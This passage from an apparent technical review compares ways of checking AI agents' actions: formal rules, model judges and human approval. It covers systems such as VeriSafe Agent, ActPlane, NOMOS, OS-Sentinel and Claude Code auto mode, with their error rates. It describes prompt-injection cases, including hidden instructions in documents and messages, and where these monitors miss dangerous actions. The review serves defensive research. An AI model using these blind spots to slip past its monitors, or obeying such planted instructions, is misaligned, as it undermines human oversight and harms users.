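| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 61.7% | 42.1% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
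| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.5% | 56.7% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 70.1% | 43.1% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 99.8% | 89.0% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

Agents could do more of their work under VeriGuard than under the judging model. How much the proofs contributed is less clear, because when Miculicich and colleagues added the parts of the system one by one, the success rate of attacks fell to zero before they added the proofs.

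VeriGuard made no errors on a benchmark in which an agent must respect different users' access rights to hospital databases. On Mind2Web-SC, where certain users are not allowed to do certain things on websites, it caught 99% to 100% of the violations, with a precision of 91.2% to 95.0%. At 91.2% precision, about one in eleven of the actions it blocked was allowed. Hand-written rules from an earlier study had a precision of 95.1% on the same benchmark but caught only 58% of the violations.

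### An exact check of a rule that may be wrong

All of these systems use a model to write the rules. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* describes Conseca as "deterministic enforcement of non-deterministic policies", and the description also fits VeriSafe Agent and Sapien. VeriSafe Agent's logic always returns the same verdict for the same rules and reported state, but the model may write different rules if it is given the same instruction twice.

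*Validating Autoformalized Specifications via Contrapuntal Languages* (2026) defines a specification as sound if it allows only what the user intended, and complete if it allows everything the user intended. A verifier misses violations when the specification is unsound and raises false alarms when it is incomplete.

The restaurant rules could have both faults. The user never says which day the reservation is for, but R1 requires today. That is usually a sensible guess, but if the user meant Friday, the verifier would block the right reservation and allow the wrong one. An agent that had correctly chosen Friday would get feedback to change the date. R3 may also be faulty because it counts the task as done as soon as the agent finds one early time that is not free, even if the restaurant has a table half an hour later.

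No program can fully test for such faults, because only the user knows what the instruction meant. *Intent Formalization* (2026) calls this the main bottleneck for formal specifications of software. The available error rates are only a rough guide to rules for agents, because they come mostly from planning, programming and mathematics, where specifications are often more complicated than "the recipient is Dana".

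*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, highlights a benchmark on which models correctly translated only 24.8% to 34.2% of descriptions into PDDL, a formal language for planning problems. Recent models do better in other settings. *SpecGuard* (2026) reports a manual audit of 60 specifications that models such as Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol wrote for programming tasks. Of these, 52 were faithful to the task, 2 were too weak and 6 were wrong. The audit covered only cases in which the system had produced a certified result, so the error rate across all attempts could be higher.

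VeriSafe Agent tries to catch translation errors by turning the rules back into English. *claimcheck* (Amster, Baker and colleagues, 2026) measured how well this kind of check works on 3,234 pairs of requirements and formal statements. In one faulty pair, the requirement was to remove the first element of a list, but the formal statement removed the last. The back-translation mentioned the last element, which made the mistake easy to spot.

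The check worked better than showing one model both versions and asking whether they agreed. Averaged over faulty and faithful statements, it was right 87.9% to 93.1% of the time, depending on the formal language, compared with 79.6% to 84.0% for the single model. It still accepted 5.5% of the faulty statements in one language and 11.6% in another, and it rejected between 8% and 22% of the faithful ones. In VeriSafe Agent, a wrong rejection only makes the model rewrite its rules, but a wrong acceptance means the agent's actions are checked against a faulty rule. A model asked directly can miss a larger share of faulty statements. *Verus-SpecGym* (Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues, 2026) found that a model acting as judge missed 26% of the faulty specifications that the paper's own tests caught.

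Lee and colleagues acknowledge that translation errors are a problem, listing "fallible intent encoding" as the first challenge in their slides. They mainly reply that VeriSafe Agent needs only one correct translation per task, whereas a reviewing model can make a new mistake at every step. This argument is good when tasks are long, because small error rates per step add up, but longer instructions also give the translator more to get wrong. Without memory, VeriSafe Agent's accuracy fell from 95.6% on the simple tasks to 88% on the harder ones.

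They also respond by repeating the whole process and taking a majority vote. With five or more votes, accuracy on the harder tasks rose from 88% to 96% without memory, and from 94% to 100% with it. Voting helps when the model's mistakes vary from one attempt to the next, so it would not help if the model assumed "today" every time.

Lee and colleagues concede that one wrong condition could stop a whole task, though they did not see this in their tests. Like Sun and colleagues, they prefer an occasional false alarm to irreversible harm. That is reasonable when a condition is too strict, but one that is too loose lets the harmful action through.

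Tiffany and colleagues respond to a more basic objection, that using one model to restrain another is circular. The model that writes a Sapien policy normally reads only the user's request and the tools' documentation, so text that an attacker plants in an email can't reach it. It also has one narrow job, whereas the agent can drift off course over many steps. Both points are convincing about attacks and drift, but an ordinary misreading is still possible. One Sapien policy checked for "London Luxury Hotel" because the user had used that name, while the database called the hotel "London Luxury".

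The isolation also cannot be complete when the user's request refers to another text, such as "do the tasks on my to-do list". Sapien leaves a gap in the policy, waits until the agent has fetched the list, and has the model write the missing rules from it. Tiffany and colleagues argue that this still follows the user's wishes, because the user chose to delegate to the list. But anyone who can edit the list can write part of the policy.

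Miculicich and colleagues accept that VeriGuard's proofs are only as good as the constraints, and say that the user has to check those by hand. Tsai and Bagdasarian suggest a similar check for Conseca, whose policies include a short reason for each rule so that a user or an expert can review them. A user who reads "the subject must contain 'urgent'" has a fair chance of noticing the mistake.

Some requests leave out a fact that can't be recovered by translating them into rules. If the inbox contains emails from two people called Bob and the user says "reply to Bob", Sapien's policy allows a reply to either, and one of them may be an attacker. Tiffany and colleagues propose that a future version detect such requests and ask the user to clarify them before it writes any rules.

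## Extending rules to many applications

Sun and colleagues wrote that rules struggle to scale, referring to the work they require. Someone has to describe each application, for example by recording that `send_email` sends data out and that its `to` field holds the recipient. They then have to write rules that use this description, and update both the description and the rules when the application or the policy changes.

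### Describing an application

Three of the systems in earlier sections divide this work very differently:

| System | Work for each new app | Work for each new task |
|---|---|---|
| MobileSafetyBench's checklists | None | A person writes a checklist |
| VeriSafe Agent | The developer declares states and triggers | A model writes the rules |
| OS-Sentinel's Formal Verifier | None | None |

Checklists take the most work over time because someone has to write a new one for each task, and it is of little use for other tasks. When Sun and colleagues ran 104 instructions live in an Android emulator, the pooled checklists gave the right verdict in only 49.3% of the runs.

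VeriSafe Agent generates its rules from the user's instruction, but it needs a description of each app. Lee and colleagues estimate that each description takes about 10 extra lines of code. They also say that each state takes 5 to 10 lines, so the three-state restaurant app in the previous section would need 15 to 30. Writing those lines is still very little work for someone who knows the app.

Those few lines have to be right, however. In one of the paper's examples, a trigger on the search button copies the search text into the restaurant's `name`. If the agent searches for restaurant R but opens restaurant S from the results, `name` still contains "R" unless the developer has added another trigger on the results.

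The developer also has to choose how much detail to declare. A delivery address has a street, a city and a postcode, and an agent fills these in one at a time. Checking after each field would raise false alarms about an unfinished address, so it makes more sense to check when the agent submits the form. But if the states leave out too much, the verifier can miss real errors. Lee and colleagues recommend starting with detailed states and removing detail where it causes false alarms, so the developer's work continues after the first 10 lines.

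The bigger obstacle is that VeriSafe Agent needs the app developer's cooperation. A company whose agents use another firm's banking app cannot add triggers to it. Lee and colleagues had this problem with 18 commercial apps, so they labeled the screens by hand. They suggest that future versions could reuse the records of app state that programming frameworks such as React Native already keep. A model could also infer the states from the screen, but they warn that its mistakes would make the verifier less reliable.

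OS-Sentinel's Formal Verifier avoids this work by applying the same file and text checks to every app. But these checks don't account for what an action means in a particular app, so the verifier flagged an agent for clearing a cache at the user's request. The verifier also depends on the phone's operating system. Sun and colleagues could collect the file data on Android without administrator access, but they say the approach is harder to apply to closed systems such as iOS.

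### Guessing what a tool does from its name

When an agent uses tool calls, the tools' names are an easily obtained description of its actions. Kekatos and colleagues tested five general obligations that rely on these names, using a keyword search to assign each tool to one or more of five types of risky action.

The researchers compared these labels with their own for 54 tools. The search assigned 30 labels, of which 27 were correct, a precision of 0.90. It should have assigned 32, so its recall was 0.84. It missed two of the six tools that send data out and two of the nine that handle payments. An earlier version labeled `get_most_recent_transactions` as a payment because the name contains "transaction", although the tool only reads data.

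These error rates look tolerable, but the choice of labels had a large effect on the verdicts. Kekatos and colleagues applied the same five obligations with four different sets of labels:

| Labels | Successful AgentDojo attacks flagged | Harmless AgentDojo runs flagged | STAC attacks flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Keywords | 70.1% | 29.3% | 71.8% |
| Keywords, corrected by hand | 79.9% | 43.9% | 73.1% |
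| Keywords, plus any hand labels they missed | 79.9% | 43.9% | 73.1% |
| Keywords, ignoring tools with more than one label | 69.0% | 26.0% | 61.7% |

The same rules flagged from 32 to 54 harmless runs out of 123. The two middle rows are identical, so the hand corrections changed the results only by adding labels that the keywords had missed. These extra labels brought more legitimate actions under the rules.

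The last row gives the results when a program ignores tools with ambiguous names. A tool called `unlock_door`, for example, would match the keywords for both removing protection and operating a device, so no rule would cover it. Ignoring such tools prevented a few false alarms but caused the program to miss about 10% more of the STAC attacks.

### What written policies require

Many software projects already contain rules for agents, written in plain English in files called `CLAUDE.md` or `AGENTS.md`. Before building ActPlane, which enforces rules in the operating system, Zheng and colleagues studied these files in 64 popular projects. They split the text into 2,116 statements, of which 1,361 were policies and the rest descriptions, such as which programming language a project uses. They then sorted the policies by what a program would have to check:

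| What a program would have to check | Share of policies | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Reasoning, communication or style, which the system can't observe | 17% | Explain your reasoning before making changes |
| The contents of a file | 38% | Use `const` instead of `let` where possible |
| A single action | 29% | Never push code directly to the main branch |
| The order of several actions, or where data goes | 16% | Run all the tests before committing |

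A program could thus check compliance with 1,127 of the policies, or 83%. But writing the check usually requires more information than the policy contains. Only 26.4% of the 1,127 are self-contained, like the ban on pushing to the main branch. Another 64.2% need information about the project, such as which command runs its tests. The remaining 9.4% depend on the current task. For example, a policy may forbid updating third-party code the project uses "without approval", and only the current conversation shows whether the user has approved it.

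About 22% of the 1,361 policies are self-contained. This quantifies the complaint about scale, since a fixed set of rules, written once and installed everywhere, could enforce only about a fifth of what these projects ask of their agents. Policies about order and data flow are the hardest to cover this way because 95% of them need outside information. These are also the policies that depend on a run's history, which is useful for reducing false alarms, as discussed in earlier sections.

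However, most of the missing information is in the project's own files, where a person or a model can look it up, which is easier than working out what a user had in mind. The study covers popular open-source projects, most of them about AI agents, so the proportions may be quite different for a bank or a hospital. Models labeled the statements, and people checked a sample of 100.

### A rule about running tests

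One project's policy says that an agent must run the tests before it commits code, which means saving a version to the project's history. Slightly shortened, the ActPlane rule is:

```
rule tests-before-commit:
  kill exec "git" "commit"
  unless after exec "go" "test" exits 0
  since write "**/*.go"
```

The second line stops the agent from committing with `git`. The third line makes an exception if the agent has run `go test` and it exited with code 0, meaning the tests passed. The last line requires the tests to have passed since the agent last changed a `.go` file. An agent that runs the tests, edits the code and then commits would break the rule, because the new version is untested.

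A general instruction to run the tests before committing doesn't mention `go test` or `.go` files. Whoever turns it into a rule has to find out that the project uses the programming language Go, and a project in another language would need a different rule. The rule also appears to accept any successful run of `go test`, even one that tests only a small part of the project. Fixing this also requires knowing how the project organizes its tests.

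Zheng and colleagues argue that the agent should write such rules itself, since it has already read the project's files. An agent can add rules for its own work but cannot weaken the ones a user or company loaded before it started. The rules also cover actions the agent takes through scripts, which tool-call checks often miss.

### Translation at three cents per policy

A model can write these rules cheaply. Of the 1,361 policies, ActPlane can enforce the 607 that concern single actions, the order of actions or data flow. An agent built on GPT-5.5 translated all 607 into rules in 34 minutes for about $17, or $0.028 each. The researchers estimate that a software engineer would cost roughly $11 per rule, or nearly $6,700 in total. Only two of the agent's rules needed a second attempt before ActPlane accepted them.

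An accepted rule is well formed but may not match the policy. To test whether rules matched, Zheng and colleagues chose 38 policies and had a model produce two compliant traces and three violating ones for each. The compliant traces were deliberately difficult. Some came close to breaking the policy, and others only looked like violations. Another model then translated the policies into rules for each system. A violation counted as corrected if the agent complied after the system intervened.

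| System | Compliant traces wrongly interrupted (of 76) | Violations corrected (of 114) |
|---|---|---|
| Text patterns on tool calls | 28 | 38 |
| FIDES | 24 | 41 |
| ActPlane without explanations | 1 | 27 |
| ActPlane | 18 | 86 |

ActPlane was much better than text patterns at catching violations, but it still wrongly interrupted 24% of the compliant traces, compared with 37% for the patterns. Zheng and colleagues attribute 17 of its 18 false alarms to overly broad translations. These rates probably overstate how often such rules would interrupt ordinary work, since few ordinary runs come as close to a violation as these traces did.

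The third row is puzzling because, if broad rules caused the false alarms, the same engine should have raised nearly as many without explanations. One possible reason is that many ActPlane rules only send the agent advice, which has no effect if the agent never receives it. Among the 607 translated policies, 66% of the rule clauses were of this type. If so, many of the 18 false alarms were misleading advice, not blocked actions.

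Models can also repair rules with little work. The researchers gave the translating model the evidence from the 28 violations that ActPlane had failed to correct and let it revise each rule once. The new rules handled 26 of the 28. But the researchers reran only those 28 traces, so they did not measure whether the revised rules would interrupt compliant traces more often. A rule that misses violations is usually too narrow, and widening it can easily cause false alarms.

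ActPlane has also been useful outside programming. Zheng and colleagues tested it on 361 workplace tasks, each asking for something with an unsafe side effect, such as leaking a password. A model wrote rules from each task's description before the agent started. Without rules, the agent did something unsafe in 106 tasks, and ActPlane prevented the unsafe action in 78 of them. Its rules also triggered in 16% of the tasks in which the agent had been safe without them. The task descriptions often named the dangerous file or command, which made these rules easier to write than rules for an ordinary request that goes wrong.

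### Defects in compiled policies

A company's policy for customer service is harder to translate than a single line about tests. Yu and colleagues built NOMOS to turn such documents into gates, and they counted what went wrong. A model read the policies for the airline and retail parts of τ²-bench five times each and proposed 79 and 53 rules. An ordinary program then looked for rules that could not work:

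| Defect in the proposed rule | Airline | Retail |
|---|---|---|
| It covers every tool, and the program can't narrow it down | 11 | 2 |
| It uses an argument that the tool doesn't have | 8 | 1 |
| It requires something that no tool in the application can provide | 5 | 0 |
| It requires the user's confirmation just to read data | 5 | 0 |
| It blocks the tool that the agent needs to satisfy it | 0 | 4 |
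| Total | 29 of 79 (36.7%) | 7 of 53 (13.2%) |

The program repaired some of these rules, for example by letting the agent use the login tools before the customer has logged in, and rejected others. This left 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules. Most of the other proposals were duplicates from the five readings (42 airline and 45 retail) rather than defective rules.

The checks greatly changed what the gate would have enforced. When Yu and colleagues turned off all the checks for a second set of proposals, 8 of the 14 airline rules and 3 of the 5 retail rules could not work. A stronger model did not solve the problem. It proposed six airline rules that used an argument their tool didn't have. It also proposed a rule requiring customers to log in, which would have blocked every action because the airline application has no login tool.

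NOMOS can find these defects without a theorem prover or another model because its rules have a restricted form. Each rule combines a tool with a condition from a fixed list, such as "the ticket is basic economy". For each type of application, a person prepares this list, along with tables showing which arguments each condition uses and which tools can satisfy it. Another person or program has to supply the code that evaluates each condition. The model connects a policy's sentences to these conditions, but people still have to describe the application.

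With the compiled rules, the share of data-changing calls that violated the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. The researchers measured this with a separate set of hand-written rules, which covered most but not all of each policy. The agent's success rate on airline tasks was 47.6% with the compiled rules and 42.8% with the hand-written ones, so automatic compilation did not make the agent less useful. Of the 40 remaining retail violations, 21 broke two clauses for which the compiler had produced no rule.

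### Replaying old runs to find bad rules

A rule can pass all these checks and still have the wrong meaning. In an early version of NOMOS for a telecom company, the policy told the agent to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. The compiler produced a rule that blocked payment requests when a bill was overdue, which is when the agent should send them.

Yu and colleagues catch such errors by replaying recordings of an agent that worked without a gate. For each tool, they count how often the rules would have blocked calls in runs where the agent completed its task. The telecom rule would have blocked 47 of 49 payment requests, or 95.9%, which is above the 90% at which NOMOS reports a problem. The rule applied the same condition to the tool that reconnects a customer's phone line, but would have blocked none of those 44 calls. A developer could therefore remove the condition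 for payment requests and keep it for reconnections.

This test needs no new runs and no model, but it finds only rules that block nearly everything. It missed a mistake in the airline rules. The policy bars passengers from changing basic economy flights but lets them change cabins on the same flights. The agent uses one tool for both kinds of change, and the compiled rule blocked that tool for every basic economy ticket. In a sample of blocked calls, all 15 that this rule stopped were requests to change only the cabin, and the researchers counted four of them as clear mistakes. Across all its rules, the gate would have blocked 31 of 43 successful calls to this tool (72.1%), too few to trigger a warning.

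The 90% threshold can't simply be much lower, because many of those blocks were intentional. The gate requires a new confirmation for every change, but the recorded agent often made several changes after a single "yes" and, unlike a live agent, can't ask again. A new application also has no recordings, so its developers would have to run an agent without protection in a test environment before using this method.

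### Moving the compiler to new applications

AgentDojo comes with no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote one page for each of its four applications and had NOMOS compile them. Each page produced three or four rules. The researchers then ran a live agent, built on a small open model, with and without the gate:

| Application | Successful attacks, no gate | Successful attacks, gate | Harmless tasks completed, no gate | Harmless tasks completed, gate |
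|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5% | 0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% | 0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |

In all four applications, the main rules check whether the user named the target of an action, such as the recipient of an email or the address of a web page. This works fairly well for banking, where the user usually names the payee or has paid them before. It fails badly on Slack. If a user asks for a summary of the article that Bob posted, the agent has to find the link in Bob's message, but the gate blocks links the user never mentioned. The rule treats Bob's link the same as an attacker's, which would also arrive in a message.

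The Slack rules stopped the attacks, but the agent could do little ordinary work under them. Rules can therefore be easy to produce but unsuited to an application. Yu and colleagues suggest estimating beforehand how well rules will suit an application from how many of its legitimate tasks act on things the agent finds by reading. They have not tested the estimate on applications they hadn't already studied.

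The new applications also needed new conditions. The list the researchers had written for banking had no way to refer to links, and 18.1% of the attacks on Slack still succeeded with that list. The researchers had to add two conditions by hand before the compiler could produce better rules.

### Keeping the rules up to date

A small change in an application can disable a rule without any error message. One compiled rule for email used an argument called `recipient`, but the email tool's argument was called `recipients`, so the rule never blocked anything. In the workspace application, five of the six connections between this condition and a tool had the same kind of fault, and attacks succeeded about as often as with no rules (7.7% and 7.3%).

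Yu and colleagues fixed this by adding a check that compares the arguments in a rule with those of the tool. The check runs only when NOMOS compiles a policy, so if a developer later renamed an argument, the rule could stop working until someone compiled the policy again. Recompiling takes only 40 model calls for the airline, so a company could do it after every software update. The company would then have to review the new rules, because two compilations of the same policy can differ. In one compilation for the travel application, a rule checked whether the user had named an event before the agent added it to the calendar. In another, the rule checked only whether the user had asked for some change, and it allowed an attacker's event.

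Changing the agent's model is easier than changing the application. Yu and colleagues used the same ten airline rules with a second model, Llama 3.3 70B, without recompiling them, and its violation rate fell from 86.9% to 7.1%. The rules refer to the airline's tools and data, which don't change with the model.

Rules that depend on the task need more frequent updates. On 21 programming tasks, ActPlane's policy-writing agent changed the rules 110 times during the work, or about five times per task. A person could not realistically review each of those changes. None of these studies followed an application through months of updates, so it is still unknown how much work the rules take to maintain over the long term.

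Automated rule-writing can turn a sentence of policy into an executable rule for about three cents. Someone must still decide which facts each application must expose, persuade its developer to expose them, and collect enough harmless runs to show when a rule is too broad. This work grows with the number of applications, and a company that skips it can end up with faulty rules.

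## Adding a model or a person to judge context

Even carefully written rules leave some questions open, such as whether the user in run C wanted the reunion organizer to have the contact list. A developer can pass these questions to a model that judges context, or to the user. Both make their own mistakes, so it matters a lot how the developer combines their verdicts with those of the rules.

### Combining two verdicts

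Suppose a rule-based verifier and a judge both check the same 100 runs with violations and 100 harmless runs. The verifier flags 50 of the runs with violations and 20 of the harmless runs, and the judge flags 60 and 10. We also assume that their mistakes are unrelated, so the judge flags 60% of the runs with violations whether or not the verifier has flagged them.

| Method | Violations flagged (of 100) | Harmless runs flagged (of 100) |
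|---|---|---|
| Rules alone | 50 | 20 |
| Judge alone | 60 | 10 |
| Flag if either objects (OR) | 80 | 28 |
| Flag only if both object (AND) | 30 | 2 |
| Rules settle clear cases, judge decides the rest | 66 | 5 |

With OR, the judge adds 60% of the 50 violations that the rules missed, bringing the total to 80. With AND, the judge confirms only 60% of the 50 that the rules caught, which leaves 30. OR always catches at least as many violations as the better of the two, but it also raises every false alarm that either one raises. AND raises only the false alarms they share, but it never catches more violations than the worse of the two.

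For the last row, the rules can also return "unsure". We assume they block 30 violations and 2 harmless runs, allow 10 violations and 68 harmless runs, and leave the other 60 violations and 30 harmless runs to the judge. The judge then reads fewer than half of the runs. Its error rates would probably be higher than in the table, though, because the cases the rules can't settle tend to be hard.

In practice, the rules and the judge rarely make unrelated mistakes. If the judge caught every violation that the rules caught, OR would flag only 60 violations instead of 80. If the violations they caught overlapped as little as possible, OR would flag all 100.

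### OS-Sentinel's combined results

OS-Sentinel flags a run if either its Formal Verifier or its contextual judge flags it. The judge is an ordinary model with a prompt that lists types of risk, such as destructive actions and privacy violations. It reads a run in windows of five steps and flags the run if it flags any window.

With Claude 4.5 Sonnet as the judge, Sun and colleagues measured an accuracy of 60.2% and an F1 of 57.1 for the judge alone, and 71.7% and 73.0 for the combination. The equations used earlier for the checklists give the underlying rates:

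| Judge's model | Detection, judge alone | False alarms, judge alone | Detection, combination | False alarms, combination |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 4.5 Sonnet | 53% | 33% | 77% | 33% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 55% | 38% | 78% | 56% |
| GPT-4o | 50% | 28% | 76% | 55% |
| GPT-4o mini | 25% | 9% | 68% | 44% |
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 53% | 40% | 81% | 66% |
| gpt-oss-120B | 55% | 40% | 78% | 62% |

With Claude 4.5 Sonnet, adding the rules caught many more violations and had no apparent downside. With GPT-4o, detection rose about as much, but false alarms nearly doubled and accuracy stayed at 60.8%. The other four models' results look more like GPT-4o's.

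The Claude 4.5 result is hard to explain. An OR combination flags every run that the Formal Verifier flags, and the GPT-4o mini row suggests that the verifier alone flags at least a third of the safe runs. The false-alarm rate could stay at 33% only if the judge and the verifier flagged almost exactly the same safe runs.

Other researchers later got results similar to those in the GPT-4o row. *Automated Trajectory Evaluation for Mobile Agents via Step-Level Consequence Reasoning and Aggregation* (2026) reran OS-Sentinel's code with GPT-4o. Adding the rules raised detection from 52% to 79%, and the precision figures imply that false alarms rose from 30% to 56%. In *SeerGuard* (2026), OS-Sentinel caught 81% of the unsafe runs and wrongly flagged about 53% of the safe ones.

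Sun and colleagues also compared OR with AND, again using Claude 4.5 Sonnet. OR had an F1 of 70.2, which implies a detection rate of about 63% and a false-alarm rate of about 17%. AND had an F1 of 52.8, which implies rates of about 37% and 4%. But OR's accuracy is 73.2% in this test and 71.7% in the main results. Its implied false-alarm rate is also lower than the rate for the judge alone in the main results, which is impossible for an OR combination that includes the same judge. The two tests must therefore have used different settings, so only the comparison between OR and AND is safe to use.

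### A judge without the user's request

Sun and colleagues' appendix states that the safety detectors never receive the user's instruction, and the printed prompts for the contextual judge don't include it. The main text, however, describes the test as if the detectors did receive it. Without the instruction, the judge can't tell a requested cache clearing, or the email in run C, from a violation.

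Zhang, Li and Chen (2026), in *MobileGrail*, built a judge for phones that does receive the user's request and keeps a short record of what the user has authorized, including details the agent had to look up. In their main example, the agent finds a recipient's number in WhatsApp at step 2 and selects a different recipient for a transfer at step 6. The judge can compare the two even though step 2 is no longer among the recent screens it receives. In our example, it could record Dana's address at step 2 and check the email against that address at step 3.

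Their training data also separates whether an action is a violation from when the judge may block, which other test sets treat as one question. An action is a violation only if it causes the harm, such as the tap that sends the money. But the judge may block earlier, starting with the first action that the user's request doesn't explain. Opening the contacts to find Dana's address is neither a violation nor a reason to block.

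Zhang and colleagues tested this on 210 unsafe runs, each paired with a harmless one. Their judge, a small model that runs on the phone, stopped 76.2% of the violations, compared with 64.5% for the same model without their training. The training had a larger effect on premature blocking, which fell from 58.6% to 5.2%. The researchers built the test with the same method as the training data, which probably improved the judge's results. But in live runs on another benchmark, the judge also cut fully successful attacks from 13 to 3 in 110 tasks, while the number of completed tasks rose from 48 to 58.

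They also criticize MobileRisk for labeling some steps unsafe when the agent only searches or browses and no harm follows. If they are right, some of OS-Sentinel's detections are false alarms, and its true error rates could be higher or lower than measured.

### Newer models as judges

The models in Sun and colleagues' tests date from 2024 and 2025. *ATBench* (2026) tested newer ones on 1,000 tool-call traces, about half of them unsafe. The judges received the whole trace, including the user's request. The false-alarm rates below follow from the published precision and recall:

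| Judge | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 87% | 40% |
| GPT-5.2 | 79% | 41% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 74% | 23% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 71% | 18% |

These judges are clearly better than the ones in OS-Sentinel, but they still flag between a fifth and two-fifths of the harmless traces. ATBench is deliberately difficult, with generated traces in which the harm often appears long after its cause. GPT-5.2 was right 90.8% of the time on the older R-Judge but only 69.0% on ATBench.

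A judge's false-alarm rate can also change sharply from one kind of task to another. *Trust No Tool* (2026) used GPT-5.4 to detect attacks in which tools return misleading results. The model caught about 76% of the malicious runs but rejected over 80% of the harmless ones, so it was more likely to reject a harmless run than a malicious one. According to the paper, the model had no sensible threshold for how much risk to accept because it hadn't been trained on examples of both malicious and harmless runs.

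Changing the judge's method can help as much as adding rules. *Automated Trajectory Evaluation* also tested a judge that first describes the effect of each step and then judges all the descriptions together. With the Qwen model, this method flagged 67% of the unsafe runs in MobileRisk and about 25% of the safe ones, while OS-Sentinel flagged 68% of the unsafe runs and 47% of the safe ones. But with GPT-4o, the same method flagged 90% of the unsafe runs and 66% of the safe ones.

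### Google's plain-language policies

Google already sells a judge of this kind. Its semantic governance policies, available as a preview in November 2026, let a model block an agent's tool calls. Administrators write the rules in ordinary English, such as a ban on automatic refunds above $75, according to Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview*. Unlike AWS, Google doesn't translate these rules into a formal language, so the model interprets them again for each call.

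The judge checks the proposed call against the user's request and against the company's rules. If the call fails either check, the system removes it from the model's response and tells the agent why. The judge bases its verdict on the user's prompt, the conversation so far, the rules, the list of tools and the proposed call.

*Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes Google's example of an agent for a finance team. The only rule forbids sending unreleased quarterly results to anyone outside the company. The judge allows an email to the company's controller and blocks one to an outside investor. Later, the agent reads a document with a hidden instruction to delete some drafts. The rule doesn't cover deletion, but the judge blocks it because the user never asked for it.

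A check against the user's request could distinguish contacts run B from runs A and C, since the user asked for the emails in A and C but not for the one in B. Google's documentation gives no error rates for the judge, so its reliability at this is unknown. A company can measure the false alarms itself in a "dry run" mode, which logs each verdict and its reason but blocks nothing.

A Google engineer whom Pogorelec quotes warns that verdicts "may vary" because a language model produces them, so an auditor can't count on reproducing an old one. A fixed rule is more reliable for a limit such as $75 and takes almost no computation to check. Google recommends using the policies alongside ordinary access controls.

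Every check also costs money and takes time. In Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies*, the sample log entry for one refund lists 1,859 tokens (the pieces of text that companies charge for when a model is used). Nearly all are input, so the cost grows as the conversation gets longer. Sun and colleagues report an average of 66 milliseconds per check with commercial models, but Zhang and colleagues measured a median of 5.1 seconds with Gemini 3.8 Flash. At that speed, checking every step of a seven-step phone task would add about 36 seconds.

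### Rules first, then a judge

Claude Code's auto mode combines rules and a judge, as in the last row of the first table. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, fixed rules allow edits inside the project folder and tools that can't change anything, such as file searches. Most other actions, including terminal commands and web requests, go to a judge. If a user has previously allowed every Python script, auto mode suspends that permission, because the judge would otherwise never check the commands that can do the most damage.

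The judge itself has two stages. A quick check answers only yes or no and leans toward blocking. If it objects, the same model considers the action again, this time with written reasoning, and the system blocks the action only if the second check objects too. This is an AND combination, and Anthropic's measurements show the expected trade:

| | Harmless calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Dangerous actions missed (52 real cases) | Data leaks missed (1,000 invented cases) |
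|---|---|---|---|
| Quick check alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both checks | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

A false-alarm rate of 0.4% is far below any in the phone tests, although it is measured per call and those rates are per run. If each call had an independent 0.4% chance of being wrongly blocked, a session of 100 calls would have a 33% chance of at least one wrong block. Anthropic argues that this is tolerable because the agent receives the reason for the block and can usually find another way. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, the system asks the user.

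The 17% is less certain because it comes from only 52 cases. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. For example, one user had said "clean up the PR", and the judge accepted this as permission to overwrite the project's shared history. The same question of consent came up in run C, and a capable model that can see the user's words still gets it wrong fairly often.

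### Keeping misleading text away from the judge

If the judge reads the same email as the agent, a hidden instruction in it can mislead both. Auto mode therefore gives the judge only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It leaves out all tool results, as well as the agent's own messages in case the agent has written a persuasive excuse.

In Anthropic's tests of other inputs, adding the agent's messages and the tool results made the judge worse at catching real dangerous actions. When the judge saw neither these nor the user's messages, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things the user had plainly requested. Including the user's messages prevented those false alarms.

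Hiding tool results also hides where a value came from. In run A, the judge would see the request to email Dana and the call to `send_email` with an address, but not the contact list that shows whose address it is. If the address doesn't contain Dana's name, the judge can't confirm that it belongs to Dana.

A rule-based program can fill this gap by looking up the address in the contact list and telling the judge only that it belongs to Dana. Instructions written into the list can't make the program report a different match. Ravindran and Deochake found that a model can use such facts well. Given the same structured facts and policy as their logical rules, the model classified all 20 of their scenarios correctly, as the rules had.

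Anthropic has since added facts of this kind. Before the agent uploads code, a check determines whether the destination is public, private or trusted, because the same upload can be routine or a leak. Anthropic made this and other changes after tests by Apollo Research, an AI safety company. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the judge then missed 7% of Apollo's artificial attacks, down from 12%. Apollo had kept some of these attacks secret, so the improvement didn't come only from fixing known examples.

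### Asking the user

The user knows best what they wanted. Sun and colleagues propose that OS-Sentinel approve ordinary actions automatically and ask a person only about the ones it flags. They argue that a false alarm causes only a pause, but this assumes that the person still pays attention when a real violation comes up.

Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts (the earlier post on auto mode gives 93%). Most of the actions are probably harmless, so the high approval rate doesn't by itself show that users are careless. To measure attention directly, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers did not know that the study was measuring their attention.

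| | Tester refused | Tester approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Judge blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Judge allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

The testers refused 13.6% of the dangerous commands, while auto mode's judge blocked 89%. Blocking every command that either the testers or the judge rejected would have stopped 943 commands, only 6 more than the judge alone. Their mistakes were also related. The testers caught 15% of the commands that the judge caught but only 5% of those it missed.

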